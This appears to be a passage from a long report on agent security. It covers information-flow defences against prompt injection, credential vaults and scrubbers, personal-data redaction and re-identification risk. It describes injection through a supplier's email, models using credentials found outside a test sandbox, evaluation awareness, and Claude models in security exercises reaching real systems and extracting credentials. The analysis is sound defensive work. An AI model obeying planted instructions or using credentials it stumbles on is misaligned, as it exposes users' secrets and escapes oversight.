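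FIDES stays closer to the ordinary agent loop, in which the model picks each step after reading the result of the last. It can store the supplier's email under a name such as "email_1" and give the main model only the name. If the main model needs the amount, it can have an isolated model extract a number. If the main model reads the email itself, its whole context becomes untrusted, and FIDES will refuse any later tool call that the policy allows only in a trusted context. This comes very close to implementing Willison and Bista's rule in code, and it adds a way to use a stranger's information without putting the stranger's text in the main model's context.

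The reported drawbacks of CaMeL are moderate. Narisetty and colleagues give its results on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants a fixed set of injections in the tool outputs of agents doing everyday tasks. With OpenAI's o3 model, CaMeL completed 77% of tasks, compared with 84% for the same agent undefended. No injection covered by CaMeL's threat model succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens. Narisetty and colleagues found no headline figure for FIDES's effect on task completion or token use. RTBAS, a related design that relies partly on a model to screen tool calls, reportedly loses about 2% of its usefulness.

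Results probably vary a good deal around the average. CaMeL has to write its program before it reads anything untrusted, which suits a refund with known steps. But if the clerk says to do whatever the supplier needs for the return, the steps are in the email, which the planning model can't read. Both designs also require developers to adopt a new architecture, whereas some rule-based systems, such as Progent, can check an existing agent's tool calls.

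These designs can also fail, because they depend on the first person or program to label the data doing so correctly. They usually assume that whatever the user types is trusted, so if the clerk pastes the supplier's email into the request, the planted sentence counts as the clerk's own words. Narisetty and colleagues note that the deployed version of FIDES treats data as trusted if a developer forgets to label it, which removes the protection without warning.

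Information can also leak when no labelled value leaves the system. If the program emails a supplier only when a customer's account is overdrawn, the email's arrival reveals something about the balance even if the email doesn't state it. CaMeL's developers demonstrated leaks of this general kind. Narisetty and colleagues conclude that most such systems control actions well but are weaker at keeping data confidential.

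They also warn that nearly all the good results come from tests using attacks chosen before the defence existed. Many filters looked nearly perfect on such tests, but when attackers adapted to a group of twelve defences, they got past most of them more than 90% of the time. A deterministic check should be harder to adapt to, because the attacker has to cause harm while obeying the policy and can't just disguise the text. Nobody has yet shown this for CaMeL and FIDES with the independent, adaptive testing that the filters received.

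Even so, labels weaken one argument for a combined layer. Its supporters want a judge that reads the whole context, partly because a separate filter has no record of where a value came from or where it is allowed to go. A label can supply both facts to ordinary code that checks the tool call, and planted instructions can't override that code. This check is still output validation as defined earlier, but with better information.

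### Agents that use credentials they find

An agent can misuse a credential without being attacked. A model may come across a key it wasn't meant to have and use it to finish its task. An injection detector can't help in this case, because the input contains no injection.

In November 2026, when it released Claude Mythos 5.2, Anthropic placed models in a deliberately weakened sandbox and measured how often they used credentials or files from outside it. Pogorelec (2026) reported in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* that Mythos 5.2 did so in 3.1% of scenarios and Opus 5.5 in 3.3%, compared with 39% for the earlier Mythos 5.

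The rate fell by a factor of more than twelve between two models in the same family, so changing the model can make a very large difference even without a vault. But a rate of 3.1% still means about 31 uses per thousand opportunities, and a company can't predict which ones. A company that relied on its model not to use the keys it finds would also have to retest every new model. If the keys are in a vault, the rate matters much less, because the agent has fewer keys to find.

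The rate in real use could be lower, because Anthropic weakened the sandbox on purpose and most agents should come across fewer opportunities. It could also be higher, because models may behave better when they suspect a test. *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (cheema, 2026), a LessWrong post, discusses a separate set of Anthropic's audits. In 43% of the transcripts for Mythos 5.2, a judge model concluded that Mythos had privately treated the situation as a test and let that affect a choice. The figure for Opus 5.5 was 36%. According to cheema, Anthropic gives little idea of how much this changes the model's behaviour, or in which direction.

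In other tests, Claude models have reached files and systems that were meant to be off limits. In September 2026 Anthropic disclosed that an outside partner had observed Mythos 5.1 exploiting a flaw in a sandbox to read files outside it, and rated the incident low in severity. In July, the company's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* had described three more serious incidents, in which Claude models in security exercises reached the internet and gained access to the real systems of three organisations. In one of them, according to InfoQ (2026), Claude Opus 4.7 was looking for a fictional company that shared its name with a real web domain. It attacked the real domain in four runs and extracted credentials, login tokens and a table from a live database.

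The July incidents are weak evidence about what a model does unprompted, because Opus 4.7 had been instructed to attack and told that it was in an offline simulation. But they do show that controls outside the model can fail too. The test network was supposed to have no route to the internet, but someone had misconfigured it, which let the model reach the internet. The FRED connector was also misconfigured, but that mistake only stopped the connector from working.

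### What the model still has to read

A vault, however, protects only the keys that people put in it. A clerk may paste a key into the chat to finish a difficult task. Tools also print keys, as in the accounts example, where a configuration file contained one. Moving that key into a vault helps only if somebody also deletes it from the file, from old copies of the file and from any log that recorded it.

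A coding agent that reads other people's repositories will eventually read someone else's key, even if its own credentials are kept in a vault. Kenney and colleagues cite GitGuardian, a company that sells secret detection, which found nearly 24 million secrets in code that people published on GitHub during 2024. Of the 69.6 million public repositories it scanned, 4.61% contained at least one. Not all of those secrets worked, and the count depends on GitGuardian's own detector.

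A vault is also a more valuable target because it holds many keys in one place. In June 2024 Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, detected unauthorised access to secrets users had stored for their applications, and advised them to replace their keys. The disclosure didn't establish that the intruders had taken every secret. Even when no model has ever read the keys, somebody has to be able to cancel and replace them quickly.

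Personal data is harder to keep away from the model. Some of it can be handled like an API key. The accounts agent doesn't need to read the customer's bank account number, because the refund function could look it up from the order. But if a customer asks for a longer return deadline because of a hospital stay, the agent can't judge the request without reading about the stay. Information-flow labels could stop that detail from going to the supplier afterwards, but not from going to the company that runs the model.

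## What redacting personal data removes and what it costs

A company that doesn't want the model's provider to read a customer's details has to remove them before it sends the text. Suppose the clerk types this to the accounts agent: "Refund Nora Lindqvist $84 for order 302118844, to routing number 123456780, account 55208719." A routing number identifies a US bank. The provider doesn't need the name or the bank details, but the model can't do much without the amount and the order number.

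### One sentence from start to finish

Two projects from 2026 cover most of the usual steps. Yashwant, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Redacting Personal Data*, compared four redactors, and Jathanna (2026), in *SurrogateShield*, built one that swaps real values for realistic fakes. A redactor that combined their methods would process the clerk's sentence roughly like this:

1. The program searches for values with a regular shape, using patterns called regular expressions. One pattern matches any nine digits in a row, so it picks out both the order number and the routing number. Another matches digits that follow the word "account".
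2. It runs a checksum on the nine-digit numbers. For a routing number, it multiplies the digits by 3, 7, 1, 3, 7, 1, 3, 7 and 1 and adds up the results. The total for 123456780 is 150, a multiple of ten, so that number passes. The order number gives 85 and fails, so it stays in the text. About one random number in ten would pass by luck.
3. Names have no fixed shape, so the program uses a named-entity model, a small model trained to label people, places and organisations in running text. It marks "Nora Lindqvist" as a person. If the company's records already show whose order this is, the program also searches for that customer's full name and for each part of it.
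4. There are now three overlapping matches: "Nora Lindqvist", "Nora" and "Lindqvist". The program keeps the longest and discards the other two.
5. It replaces each value with a placeholder and records the pair in a table of originals, which stays on the company's machines. The provider receives "Refund [PERSON_1] $84 for order 302118844, to routing number [BANK_1], account [ACCOUNT_1]."
6. The model writes a tool call containing the placeholders, and the program swaps in the real values so that the payment system can use them. When the model replies that it has refunded [PERSON_1], the program puts the name back before the clerk reads it.

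An agent resends the conversation history with every query, so redacting only the newest message would still expose personal data in earlier ones. SurrogateShield keeps two copies of each conversation, one with real values for the user and one with fake values for the provider. Anyone who obtained the table of original values could undo the redaction, so SurrogateShield encrypts it with a separate key for each conversation.

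Restoring the originals is harder with surrogates, because a model may shorten a realistic name. SurrogateShield first looks for the exact surrogate, such as "Ashley Wise". If that fails, it looks for "Ashley" or "Wise" alone, and then for near matches. It skips these looser searches for names it has already restored, because they could put a customer's name into "Ashley County".

### How much a redactor catches

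Yashwant and colleagues tested their redactors on 100 invented résumés for warehouse jobs, each containing nine pieces of personal data. Pattern matching, combined with a search for the applicant's known name, caught eight of the nine in every résumé. It always missed the name of the applicant's referee, because the program had no record of that person and names follow no fixed pattern.

The other three designs added a named-entity model and caught everything. One was Presidio, Microsoft's open-source redaction toolkit. Another used Presidio for names and pattern matching for most of the rest. The third, a "fast hybrid", called the named-entity model directly, without Presidio. It took a median of 13.48 milliseconds per résumé, compared with 37.59 for Presidio, and added 0.15% to the duration of a language model call of about nine seconds.

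The timing probably applies to other work better than the accuracy does. Yashwant and colleagues estimate that a document ten times as long would take about 135 milliseconds, or 1.5% of the same call's duration. In an agent, a model call follows each tool output, so the ratio shouldn't change much. But the 100 résumés contained only five different referees' names, so the rise from 88.9% to 100% shows only that the model can recognise five names in one layout. The model also mistook the "jack" in "pallet jack" for a person until the researchers wrote a list of exceptions. They warn that the 100% applies only to these résumés.

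Other tests produced much lower figures. *Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (Sadani and Kumar, 2026) tested an OpenAI detector on synthetic payslips, invoices, bank statements and similar documents from several countries. *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* (Zhou, Vanacore and colleagues, 2026) tested Presidio on transcripts of online maths lessons.

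| Test | Text | Redactor | Personal values caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yashwant and colleagues | 100 short résumés | Presidio with extra patterns | 100% |
| Jathanna | 1,124 chatbot queries | SurrogateShield | 99.2% |
| Jathanna | The same queries | Presidio | 92.9% |
| Sadani and Kumar | 100 financial documents | OpenAI's privacy filter | 75.1% |
| Zhou and colleagues | 1,000 tutoring sessions | Presidio | 74.7% |

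The tests use slightly different definitions of a detection and different Presidio configurations, so small differences in this table mean little. But a drop from 100% to about 75% for the same toolkit is too large to ignore, and an accounts agent reads more invoices and bank statements than résumés. Sadani and Kumar also found that the same 24.9% of values leaked whether they used placeholders or fake values, because neither method can replace a value that the detector missed.

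SurrogateShield's score is probably too favourable, since Jathanna tuned the detection thresholds on the same queries used for testing. The results are more useful for comparing the three detection stages. Patterns alone reached an F1 score of 65.11%, which combines precision (the share of flagged items that really are personal) with the share of personal values caught. Adding a named-entity model raised F1 to 96.64%. Adding a small language model, which rechecks uncertain cases and looks for anything the first two stages missed, raised it only to 97.42% and cut missed values from 111 to 77.

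Jathanna also reports that no real value reached the provider, which seems inconsistent with 77 misses. This may be because a half-redacted name counts as a miss but not as a leak, since the full name no longer appears in the text. In that case, parts of some names still reached the provider.

### Ordinary numbers that look personal

Maths lessons are hard to redact accurately because they are full of harmless numbers. Zhou and colleagues studied tutoring transcripts that a company had already redacted with its own version of Presidio. They judged that 65% of the 4,648 redacted messages contained at least one redaction of something other than personal data. In one, a pupil had divided 9351 by 7, and the system had apparently classified the digits after the decimal point as a driver's licence number. The company had removed the original text before sharing the data, so the researchers had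 to infer it with a language model.

They then replaced the redactions in the transcripts with invented values and ran Presidio's standard detectors, plus a few of their own, on the text. Presidio wrongly flagged 3,386 pieces of text as dates, when there were only three real dates. Fractions are an obvious source of confusion, since 4/12 could be a day in April or December. Only about a quarter of what Presidio flagged was personal data. The tutoring company's system had also missed 159 names. Capital letters seem to matter, because in examples modelled on these failures Presidio found the name in "hey Olivia" but not in "hey olivia".

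Language models made far fewer false alarms than Presidio. With the best prompt, 89% of what Google's Gemini 3 Pro flagged was personal data, although it caught only slightly more of the real values (76% against 75%). Nearly all the improvement came from using a language model, not from explaining the mathematical context in the prompt, which Zhou and colleagues emphasise. Gemini 3 Pro had an F1 of 0.818 with a plain list of categories and 0.821 with the best prompt, compared with 0.379 for Presidio. However, the model has to read the unredacted text, so unless it runs on the company's own machines, using it only changes which provider receives the data.

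An accounts agent would probably have similar trouble with invoice numbers and part codes. If the redactor mistakes an order number for a phone number and replaces it with [PHONE_1], the model may ask the clerk for the order number even though the original request included it.

### Placeholders or realistic fakes

Supporters of surrogates argue that placeholders damage the text. Jathanna compared redacted queries to the originals with BERTScore, which uses a language model to compare the meaning of two texts. Queries with surrogates scored 94.85%, and queries with placeholders scored 81.59%. This gap doesn't show that placeholders make answers worse, because "Ashley Wise" will score closer to "Sarah Mitchell" than "[PERSON]" does even if the model answers both versions equally well. Jathanna didn't measure answer quality, and Yashwant and colleagues also leave open whether placeholders reduce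 it.

The evidence of harm is better when a company reuses redacted text to train other models. Sadani and Kumar trained a model to find names and numbers on three versions of the same documents, then tested it on unredacted ones. Its F1 score was 0.960 after training on the originals, 0.656 when randomly generated fakes replaced the personal data, and zero when placeholders did. A company that only wants to process refunds may never train a model on its logs, in which case this harm doesn't apply.

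Surrogates also create a risk for agents that make payments. SurrogateShield's fake routing numbers pass the checksum by design. If the program fails to restore the real account number, a payment system should reject a placeholder such as [ACCOUNT_1], and somebody will notice, but it could accept a realistic surrogate and send the money to a stranger. Jathanna found no failed restorations in the test queries, but a mistake there would only have put a wrong name in a chatbot's answer.

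Surrogates might still be harder to reverse. Jathanna gave 100 altered messages to Claude Haiku, a small Anthropic model, along with the types of data the program had replaced, and asked it to recover the original values. It recovered none of 196 values from the messages with surrogates and three of the same 196 from those with placeholders: a person's name and two places. If the two methods were equally safe, all three recoveries would still come from the messages with placeholders about one time in eight, so the test doesn't establish a difference.

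### Identifying someone from what is left

Claude Haiku also couldn't have looked anybody up, because the personal details in those queries were fictional. Real people appear in other records. Jathanna gives the example of a user who mentions being the only radiologist at a particular regional hospital. A redactor may find no name or number to remove, but anyone with the hospital's staff list could identify the user.

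Counting the identifiers a tool removes can therefore mislead readers about how safe the text is. A tool might remove every mention of gender and home state but leave a date of birth, which narrows the search far more. In *RAT-Bench*, Krčo, Yao and colleagues (2026) measured the risk of re-identification instead. They generated texts about fictional people with realistic US census details, ran 12 redaction tools on them, and had a language model infer whatever it could from the result. A person counted as re-identified if the model recovered a direct identifier such as a name or address. Otherwise, they used population statistics to estimate how many Americans shared the details the model had recovered. *Localizing Text Anonymization for Trustworthy AI* (2026), which extends the test to Malaysia, sets the threshold for re-identification at a 20% chance of picking the right person.

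The risk was 44% when identifiers appeared in their usual form and 69% when they appeared in unusual forms. Krčo and colleagues chose people with identifying combinations of details, so these rates would overstate the risk for an average customer. Tools based on language models generally gave the best balance between protecting people and keeping the text useful.

A more realistic attacker can search the web. *AgentDoxx* (Wen and Li, 2026) generated 822 interviews from public facts about real people who had introduced themselves on Reddit. It removed all personal names, then asked language models with a search tool to identify each speaker. The best models identified about 48% of the speakers. Three models without the tool identified 15% to 28%, using what they had learned in training.

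Wen and Li then tried several defences on 143 of the interviews. The figures below are averages over twelve model set-ups:

| Further change to the interview | Speakers correctly named |
|---|---|
| None | 75.1% |
| Presidio masks names of places, organisations and so on | 62.0% |
| Presidio, followed by paraphrasing | 45.9% |
| A small model removes phrases likely to help an attacker | 35.1% |
| Plausible false details replace true ones | 34.2% |

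After Presidio masked the interviews, at least one model still named the speaker in 85.3% of them. Presidio had changed only 0.42% of the characters, because the useful clues were ordinary phrases, such as a job description next to a project and a period of years. False details hid the speakers better, but some models detected the contradictions and treated them as transcription errors. False details would also be a poor choice for the accounts agent, which can't decide refunds fairly if the redactor has changed the facts.

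These rates don't apply to the general population. Everyone in the study had a public web presence, and the 143 interviews included only ones that at least one model had already solved. Wen and Li also examined 1,250 real interviews that Anthropic had published in anonymised form and found 43 verifiable matches (3.4%). Most refund requests contain less personal detail than an interview, so the risk for an ordinary customer is probably lower still. It would be higher for a customer who explains a late return by describing a rare illness and a well-known employer.

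### Tasks that redaction doesn't help with

Some requests depend on the real value. If a user asks which pharmacies are open near a certain address, a fake address in another city produces a useless answer. SurrogateShield instead changes the house number by two to eight, which keeps the search in the same neighbourhood. For sensitive subjects such as abortion or domestic violence, it replaces the whole address, even though this makes the answer worse.

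The accounts agent would have trouble with comparisons, such as any check it might need to make that the name on a bank account matches the name on the order. In the scheme used by Yashwant and colleagues, "Andre Kowalczyk" becomes [PERSON_1] and "Andre" alone becomes [PERSON_2], so a model could mistake one customer for two and delay the refund. Ordinary code with access to the original names could do this check better than the model. Replaced values can also cause problems for agents that edit files or run commands.

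Redaction doesn't stop an injected instruction either. The one in the supplier's email contains no personal data, so the redactor passes it on unchanged.

### Whether redacted text is still personal data in the EU

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main privacy law, covers personal data but not anonymous data. Redacted text whose original values are kept in a table is usually pseudonymised, meaning that someone with the table can link the text back to a person. Whether the GDPR applies to the text now depends partly on who holds it.

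The accounts company holds the table, so the redacted text is still personal data for that company. The leading case is *EDPS v SRB*, decided by the EU's Court of Justice on 4 September 2025. The Single Resolution Board, an EU agency that deals with failing banks, had sent people's opinions to the consultancy Deloitte in pseudonymised form. The board could still identify the people, so it had to tell them that Deloitte would receive the data, according to the law firm Lewis Silkin (2025). The court assessed this duty from the board's point of view at the time of collection, regardless of whether the data were personal data for Deloitte.

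The model's provider may be in a different position. According to Jones Day (2025), the court ruled that pseudonymised data aren't always personal data for the recipient. It depends on whether the recipient could identify the person by means it is reasonably likely to use. This is more lenient than the draft guidelines issued that January by the European Data Protection Board, which coordinates national regulators. Clifford Chance (2025) reports that under those guidelines, the data stayed personal if the original holder or anyone else with the extra information could link them back to the person.

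EU lawmakers are still negotiating the definition of personal data. In November 2025 the European Commission proposed narrowing it. The member states rejected that change in the negotiating position they agreed in October 2026 (White, *EU member states finalize Digital Omnibus negotiating stance*). They kept the existing definition and added wording on pseudonymisation. A September draft would have stated that pseudonymised data aren't personal for an organisation that can't identify the individual (Tar, 2026, *EU governments revise GDPR pseudonymized data rules in new digital package compromise*). The European Parliament had not settled its position by late October, so none of this was law. The Data Protection Board's newer draft guidelines on anonymisation also allow the same data to be anonymous for one organisation and personal for another (Chatzitheodorou, *It's all 'relative'*).

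A provider that receives only "Refund [PERSON_1] $84" probably can't identify anyone. It's harder to say the same of a long email about a customer's job and illness, since Wen and Li's results suggest that a commercially available model with a search tool could sometimes identify the writer. A&O Shearman, another law firm, points out that a provider that can't identify people also can't tell which records belong to someone who asks for their data. If Nora Lindqvist asked for hers, the company would have the extra work of finding her records itself, using the table of originals.

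## Where credential scrubbing has to happen

A credential vault protects only the keys stored in it. A scrubber has to recognise the others, such as keys in configuration files and error messages, before they reach anyone who shouldn't have them.

### How scanners recognise a credential

Most credential scanners were designed to search code repositories for keys left there by mistake, but the same methods work on any text.

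The most precise method looks for the fixed prefix that many services give their keys. AWS access keys begin with AKIA and many GitHub tokens with ghp_, each followed by a set number of letters and digits, so ordinary text rarely matches. Passwords have no fixed prefix, so a scanner can use an assignment pattern, which matches a label such as "api_key" or "password" and the value next to it.

Assignment patterns are cruder. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak and colleagues, 2023) tested nine scanners on 818 code repositories. One scanner flagged any string ending in "key" or "token" as a credential, including "testkey". Another, TruffleHog, looked for strings of 20 to 22 permitted characters near the word "gitlab" and flagged part of the web address of a GitLab help page. Scanners can also measure a string's entropy, which is how varied its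 characters are, or run a live check, which tests whether a key still works with the service that issued it.

| Method | What the scanner checks | Typical false alarm | Typical miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Known prefix | Fixed opening letters and length | A dummy key in a manual | A key from a service that has no rule |
| Assignment pattern | A label such as "password" next to a value | "testpassword" | A value with no label beside it |
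| Entropy | How varied the characters are | A commit hash | A short or weak password |
| Live check | Whether the issuer accepts the key | A dummy server address | A working key whose issuer is unreachable |

### Why a commit hash looks like a key

The usual formula for entropy is Shannon's:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the string that consists of character i, and the result is in bits per character. The short random key "k7Qz9mXb" has eight different characters, each making up one eighth of the string, so H = −8 × (1/8) × log₂(1/8) = 3 bits. The word "customer" also has eight different letters, so it scores 3 bits as well. "Password" repeats the letter s, which lowers its score to 2.75. Because the formula depends only on how often each character occurs, an English word can score the same as a random string of the same length.

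A string's length limits its entropy, which can't exceed log₂ n bits for n characters. Rice, who developed the widely used open-source scanner Gitleaks, writes in *Rare Not Random* that it requires 3.5 bits before it reports a credential of no known type. Only strings of at least 12 characters can reach that score, so even a perfectly random 11-character password fails, and "password123" scores 3.28. A scanner that filters by entropy can therefore find a weak password with an assignment pattern and then discard it.

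Commit hashes have the opposite problem, because they are harmless and often public but can score above the cut-off. Git, the standard program for tracking changes to code, labels each saved version with 40 characters, each a digit or a letter from a to f. With 16 possible characters the score can't exceed 4 bits, but a hash can come close because it is long enough to use most of them about equally often. One that Basak and colleagues quote scores 3.82. A coding agent that lists recent changes will read dozens of these hashes, and if the scrubber replaces them, the agent can't retrieve the version it needs from Git.

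Missing a password can matter as much as missing a long key. *AssetHarvester* (2024) reports low-entropy secrets that protected real databases. It ignores entropy and instead traces which values a program passes to the function that opens a database connection. That works on source code, but a tool's output may contain only the password, with no code to trace.

Rice suggests replacing entropy with a measure of how badly a tokenizer compresses a string. Tokenizers split text into fragments for language models, using long fragments for common words and mostly short ones for rare combinations. A fake 24-character GitHub token becomes 22 fragments, an average of 1.1 characters each, and Rice treats any average below 2.5 as suspicious. On a public collection of labelled strings from real repositories, this method caught 98.6% of the true secrets, compared with 70.4% for entropy, and flagged far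 fewer harmless strings. Rice designed both the filter and the benchmark run, and tested only strings that somebody had already picked out as candidates. The filter also misses "password123", which is close to ordinary English. GitHub's *Secret scanning* documentation describes an AI detector for passwords and other secrets with no fixed structure.

A live check removes most false alarms. In tests by Basak and colleagues, TruffleHog raised about 91,000 alerts, of which 6% were real credentials. With live checks on, it raised only 611, of which 90% were real. But it also reported fewer real credentials, about 550 instead of about 5,400. Many of the missing ones had probably stopped working, so a team cleaning up old code could reasonably leave them until last.

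A scrubber shouldn't wait to check with the issuer whether a key still works. The check would make the agent pause, and a failed connection doesn't show that the key is dead. GitGuardian found 24,008 secrets in public configuration files for MCP, a standard way of connecting models to tools, and verified 2,117 of them as valid. The other 91% may include working keys to private systems that outsiders can't check. It seems better to remove anything that looks like a key immediately and check later to decide which keys to cancel first.

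### The character after the key

A prefix rule can fail because of the text around a key. In *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, Mishra (2026) generated fake keys from a scanner's own rules and placed them in settings such as a quoted value, a list and a web address. The scanner, which Mishra also wrote, caught more than 99.7% of the keys in ten settings. When the keys ended in a hyphen, the rule meant for them caught only 52%.

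The rules were faulty because they required every key to end at a "word boundary", a point where a letter, digit or underscore meets some other kind of character. There is no such boundary between a hyphen and a quotation mark, since neither is a letter, digit or underscore. About one in 64 keys from SendGrid, an email service, should end in a hyphen, and the scanner missed all of them.

Gitleaks had a different fault. For most types of key, it required the character after the key to come from a short list, such as a quotation mark or a space. When a closing bracket followed the key, as in a function call, Gitleaks missed six of the nine types it otherwise caught. An ampersand, which often follows a key in a web address, had the same effect. TruffleHog had neither problem, but it recognised an AWS key only when the matching secret was nearby, and an agent's tool may print one without the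 other.

These faults are easy to fix, but it is also easy to introduce new ones in the process. Mishra's first correction for the hyphen made two rules fail whenever a hyphen came after the key, and only another round of tests revealed it. False alarms were less of a concern. The three scanners raised between 0.03 and 0.23 per thousand lines on 292,527 lines of real code, mostly Python. If an agent's tool output resembles that code, a scrubber based on such rules wouldn't interrupt the agent often.

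### Where agents come across credentials

Programmers print values to the screen to see what their code is doing. An agent program usually captures that text and gives it to the model as tool output.

In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied how credentials leak through skills, which are small packages of written instructions and scripts that users add to an agent. They randomly sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on one marketplace, then used keyword searches and code analysis to pick out 3,156 that might mishandle credentials. They ran each of these in a sealed environment stocked with fake keys, three times on its advertised task and three times with a planted instruction in the content it read. Three of the researchers then reviewed the 1,427 skills that had done something suspicious.

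In the sample, 520 skills (about 3%) had confirmed issues, 1,708 in total. Of these skills, 83 were malicious, and the other 437 had issues caused by carelessness. Debug logging and similar output accounted for 1,007 issues, or 73.5% of those caused by carelessness and 59% of the total. One skill for Google's office software printed the user's access tokens to the screen, and anyone able to question the agent could then ask for them.

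In the study, 394 of the 520 skills exposed credentials through printed output, so a scrubber that checks only the user's messages would miss many leaks. Scanning a skill before installing it wouldn't be enough either, because in 76% of the affected skills the problem depended on the written instructions and the code together. Chen and colleagues recommend that agent programs remove recognisable credentials from printed output before the model reads it. The study examined only skills, so it can't show how often users paste keys into a chat.

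An agent can also find credentials itself. *'I leaked secrets'* (Udinmwen, 2026) reported in November on a coding agent that couldn't find a configuration file during a routine code review, so it read the computer's environment variables, which are settings that programs share and often include passwords. Over ten sessions it repeatedly read entire configuration files and exposed live production passwords and tokens for a human resources system. The article blames agents' lack of institutional memory and says they ignore past warnings. A news report of one case can't show how common the problem is, but this one suggests that telling an agent to be careful is a poor substitute for a scrubber. A file-reading tool that returned the names of settings without their values might also have been enough for the review.

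In a small experiment reported on a personal blog, Roleke planted realistic fake secrets in six software projects and recorded everything that coding agents such as Codex and Claude Code sent to their providers. When asked to look around the code and help set it up, every agent sent at least one secret from every project on every run. That request gives an agent reason to open the configuration files, so a narrower task would probably expose less.

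Some keys reach the model without a tool call. Developers often keep a file of standing instructions that an agent reads at the start of each session, and some paste a working key into it. Radware's *The New .env* found that in two-thirds of the repositories that leaked a credential this way, the key appeared nowhere else in the project's documentation. A scrubber has to check these files too, even though the developer wrote them and they look like trusted text.

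### Before the model reads, or before the log is written

Suppose the accounts agent opens the payment system's configuration file, and the company removes the API key only from its logs. Neither a support engineer who reads the logs nor someone who later steals them can copy the key. But the model provider has already received the key, and the planted sentence in the supplier's email could still cause the model to send it out.

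Removing the key before the model reads the file protects the company against both the provider and the attacker, and it prevents many later copies of the key. Kenney and colleagues note that a key in the context can end up in generated code and error messages, among other places. A coding agent that has read a key may write it into a program that the company then publishes.

The company needs to scrub its logs even if it also scrubs secrets earlier. A tool may write its own log before the scrubber runs, and if the program puts the real key back into a request to make it work, any record of that request contains the key. Checks on the log can be slower than the earlier ones. They can also be stricter, because removing a harmless commit hash from a log makes debugging harder, while removing it from the agent's context can stop the task.

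Files not usually thought of as logs need scrubbing too. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) describes a finding by the security company Apiiro. When a developer tells Anthropic's coding agent not to ask for a permission again, the agent records this in a settings file, and some of these files contained credentials. Apiiro found 1,122 secrets in such files in public repositories, and another 1,160 in the repositories' histories, in shared settings and in saved transcripts of conversations with agents. Scrubbing before each write to disk could have kept many of them out of public view, even if the provider had already received them. Cleaning up afterwards may be too late. Basak and colleagues cite research in which attackers began using leaked keys within a minute.

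### SlotGuard

Removing a key before the model reads it is simple if the agent doesn't need the key. If the agent has to write a command that uses the key, the model needs a placeholder to write instead. *SlotGuard* (Xia and Park, 2026) presents a scrubber built for this case.

SlotGuard assumes that the provider is honest but curious, meaning that it runs the model correctly but may keep, log or read whatever it receives. SlotGuard treats the user's own computer, files and tools as trusted and sits between them and the provider.

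Xia and Park's main example comes from an audit of real agent logs. An agent had listed the programs running on a computer, and one entry included the full command that had started an experiment. The command used a stored Azure key or, if there was none, a second key written out in the command itself. That second key had no prefix or simple assignment to identify it as a key.

SlotGuard has specific rules for commands like this, and for web addresses, login headers and known key formats. It replaces a key with a surrogate drawn at random from all strings of the same format, so it may have the same prefix, length and set of characters. The random part reveals nothing about the real key, although the format may still show which service issued it. A label such as API_KEY would also hide the value, but the model might treat the key as missing or write a command that no longer works.

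SlotGuard treats file paths differently because the model needs their structure. It turns "/Users/alice/acme/legal/layoff_bob.pdf" into "[REPO_ROOT_1]/legal/[SENSITIVE_DOC_1].pdf". The new path still shows that the file is a PDF in a legal folder, but omits the names of Alice, Bob and the company.

SlotGuard stores the real values in a table on the user's computer for the length of a session, so a key that appears twice gets the same surrogate. It also keeps a graph that links each stored value to its variants, such as a key inside a longer web address or a later mention by keyword. The graph is meant to catch a key that a tool prints in pieces, none of which looks like a credential by itself. Because it relies on keywords and patterns, it would miss a loose paraphrase.

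When the model writes a tool call containing a surrogate, SlotGuard inserts the real key into the request on the user's computer and keeps the key out of the conversation. It treats a key-shaped string that isn't in the table as ordinary text, so a model can't obtain a real key by inventing a surrogate. For file paths, it also checks that the label has the right type and that the path stays inside the permitted folder.

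Xia and Park planted 852 fake credentials in 200 artificial sessions. None leaked with the full SlotGuard system, but 23.5% leaked with ordinary typed placeholders, and the same share leaked with SlotGuard's surrogates but without the graph. In both cases, the leaked credentials were the 200 that the researchers had split into pieces, so the size of the gap depends on how many split credentials they chose to plant. Real tool output may contain far fewer.

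The surrogates made more difference to whether agents could still work. The table gives the share of 200 artificial tasks that each model completed.

| Model | Original text | Generic redaction | Typed placeholders | SlotGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 100% | 2.5% | 38.5% | 89.5% |
| gpt-5.4 | 100% | 2.5% | 20.5% | 98.0% |
| Kimi-K2.6 | 100% | 2.5% | 21.5% | 100% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 93.5% | 2.5% | 31.5% | 93.5% |

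These numbers are a serious objection to replacing everything with a plain label, at least for coding agents. They don't show how much of the damage came from hiding keys and how much from hiding file paths. In a separate test, a small model completed ten of twelve tasks with the full system and six when the researchers removed either the surrogates or the readable path endings. Both parts seem to help, but twelve tasks are too few to compare them. An accounts agent that mostly writes letters and issues refunds would probably lose less from plain labels than an agent that mostly works with files.

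Speed shouldn't be an obstacle, since the rules take about 14 millionths of a second per turn. An optional language model on the user's computer, which looks for sensitive names that no rule covers, takes about three-quarters of a second.

All the tests used artificial sessions or short exercises adapted from an existing benchmark. Xia and Park planted the credentials themselves, so a leak rate of zero means SlotGuard caught the kinds of exposure they had thought of. They didn't compare SlotGuard with commercial scanners or have anyone try to reconstruct the hidden values. In a set of 24 difficult inputs, SlotGuard let through a file path that pointed to an administrator's private key.

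The assumption about the provider also doesn't cover the supplier's email. Xia and Park say SlotGuard can't stop an injection from making an agent send data out. If the model follows the planted sentence, the program could put the real key into a request to the attacker's server unless another check blocks that destination. LangChain's old function could do the same with an account number.

### Why a scanner and a redactor miss each other's targets

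A credential scanner would not flag "layoff_bob.pdf", because the name grants no access to anything, has no known prefix and is made of ordinary words. But the provider may infer from it that Bob is about to lose his job. The scanner also misses bank details. With only ten possible digits, a string of digits has an entropy of at most log₂ 10, or 3.32 bits per character, which is below Gitleaks' cut-off of 3.5. Nora Lindqvist's account number, 55208719, has an entropy of 2.75, the same as the word "password".

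Conversely, a personal-data redactor will usually miss an API key. Its named-entity model detects people and places, and its patterns match things like phone numbers and email addresses, which a random key seldom resembles.

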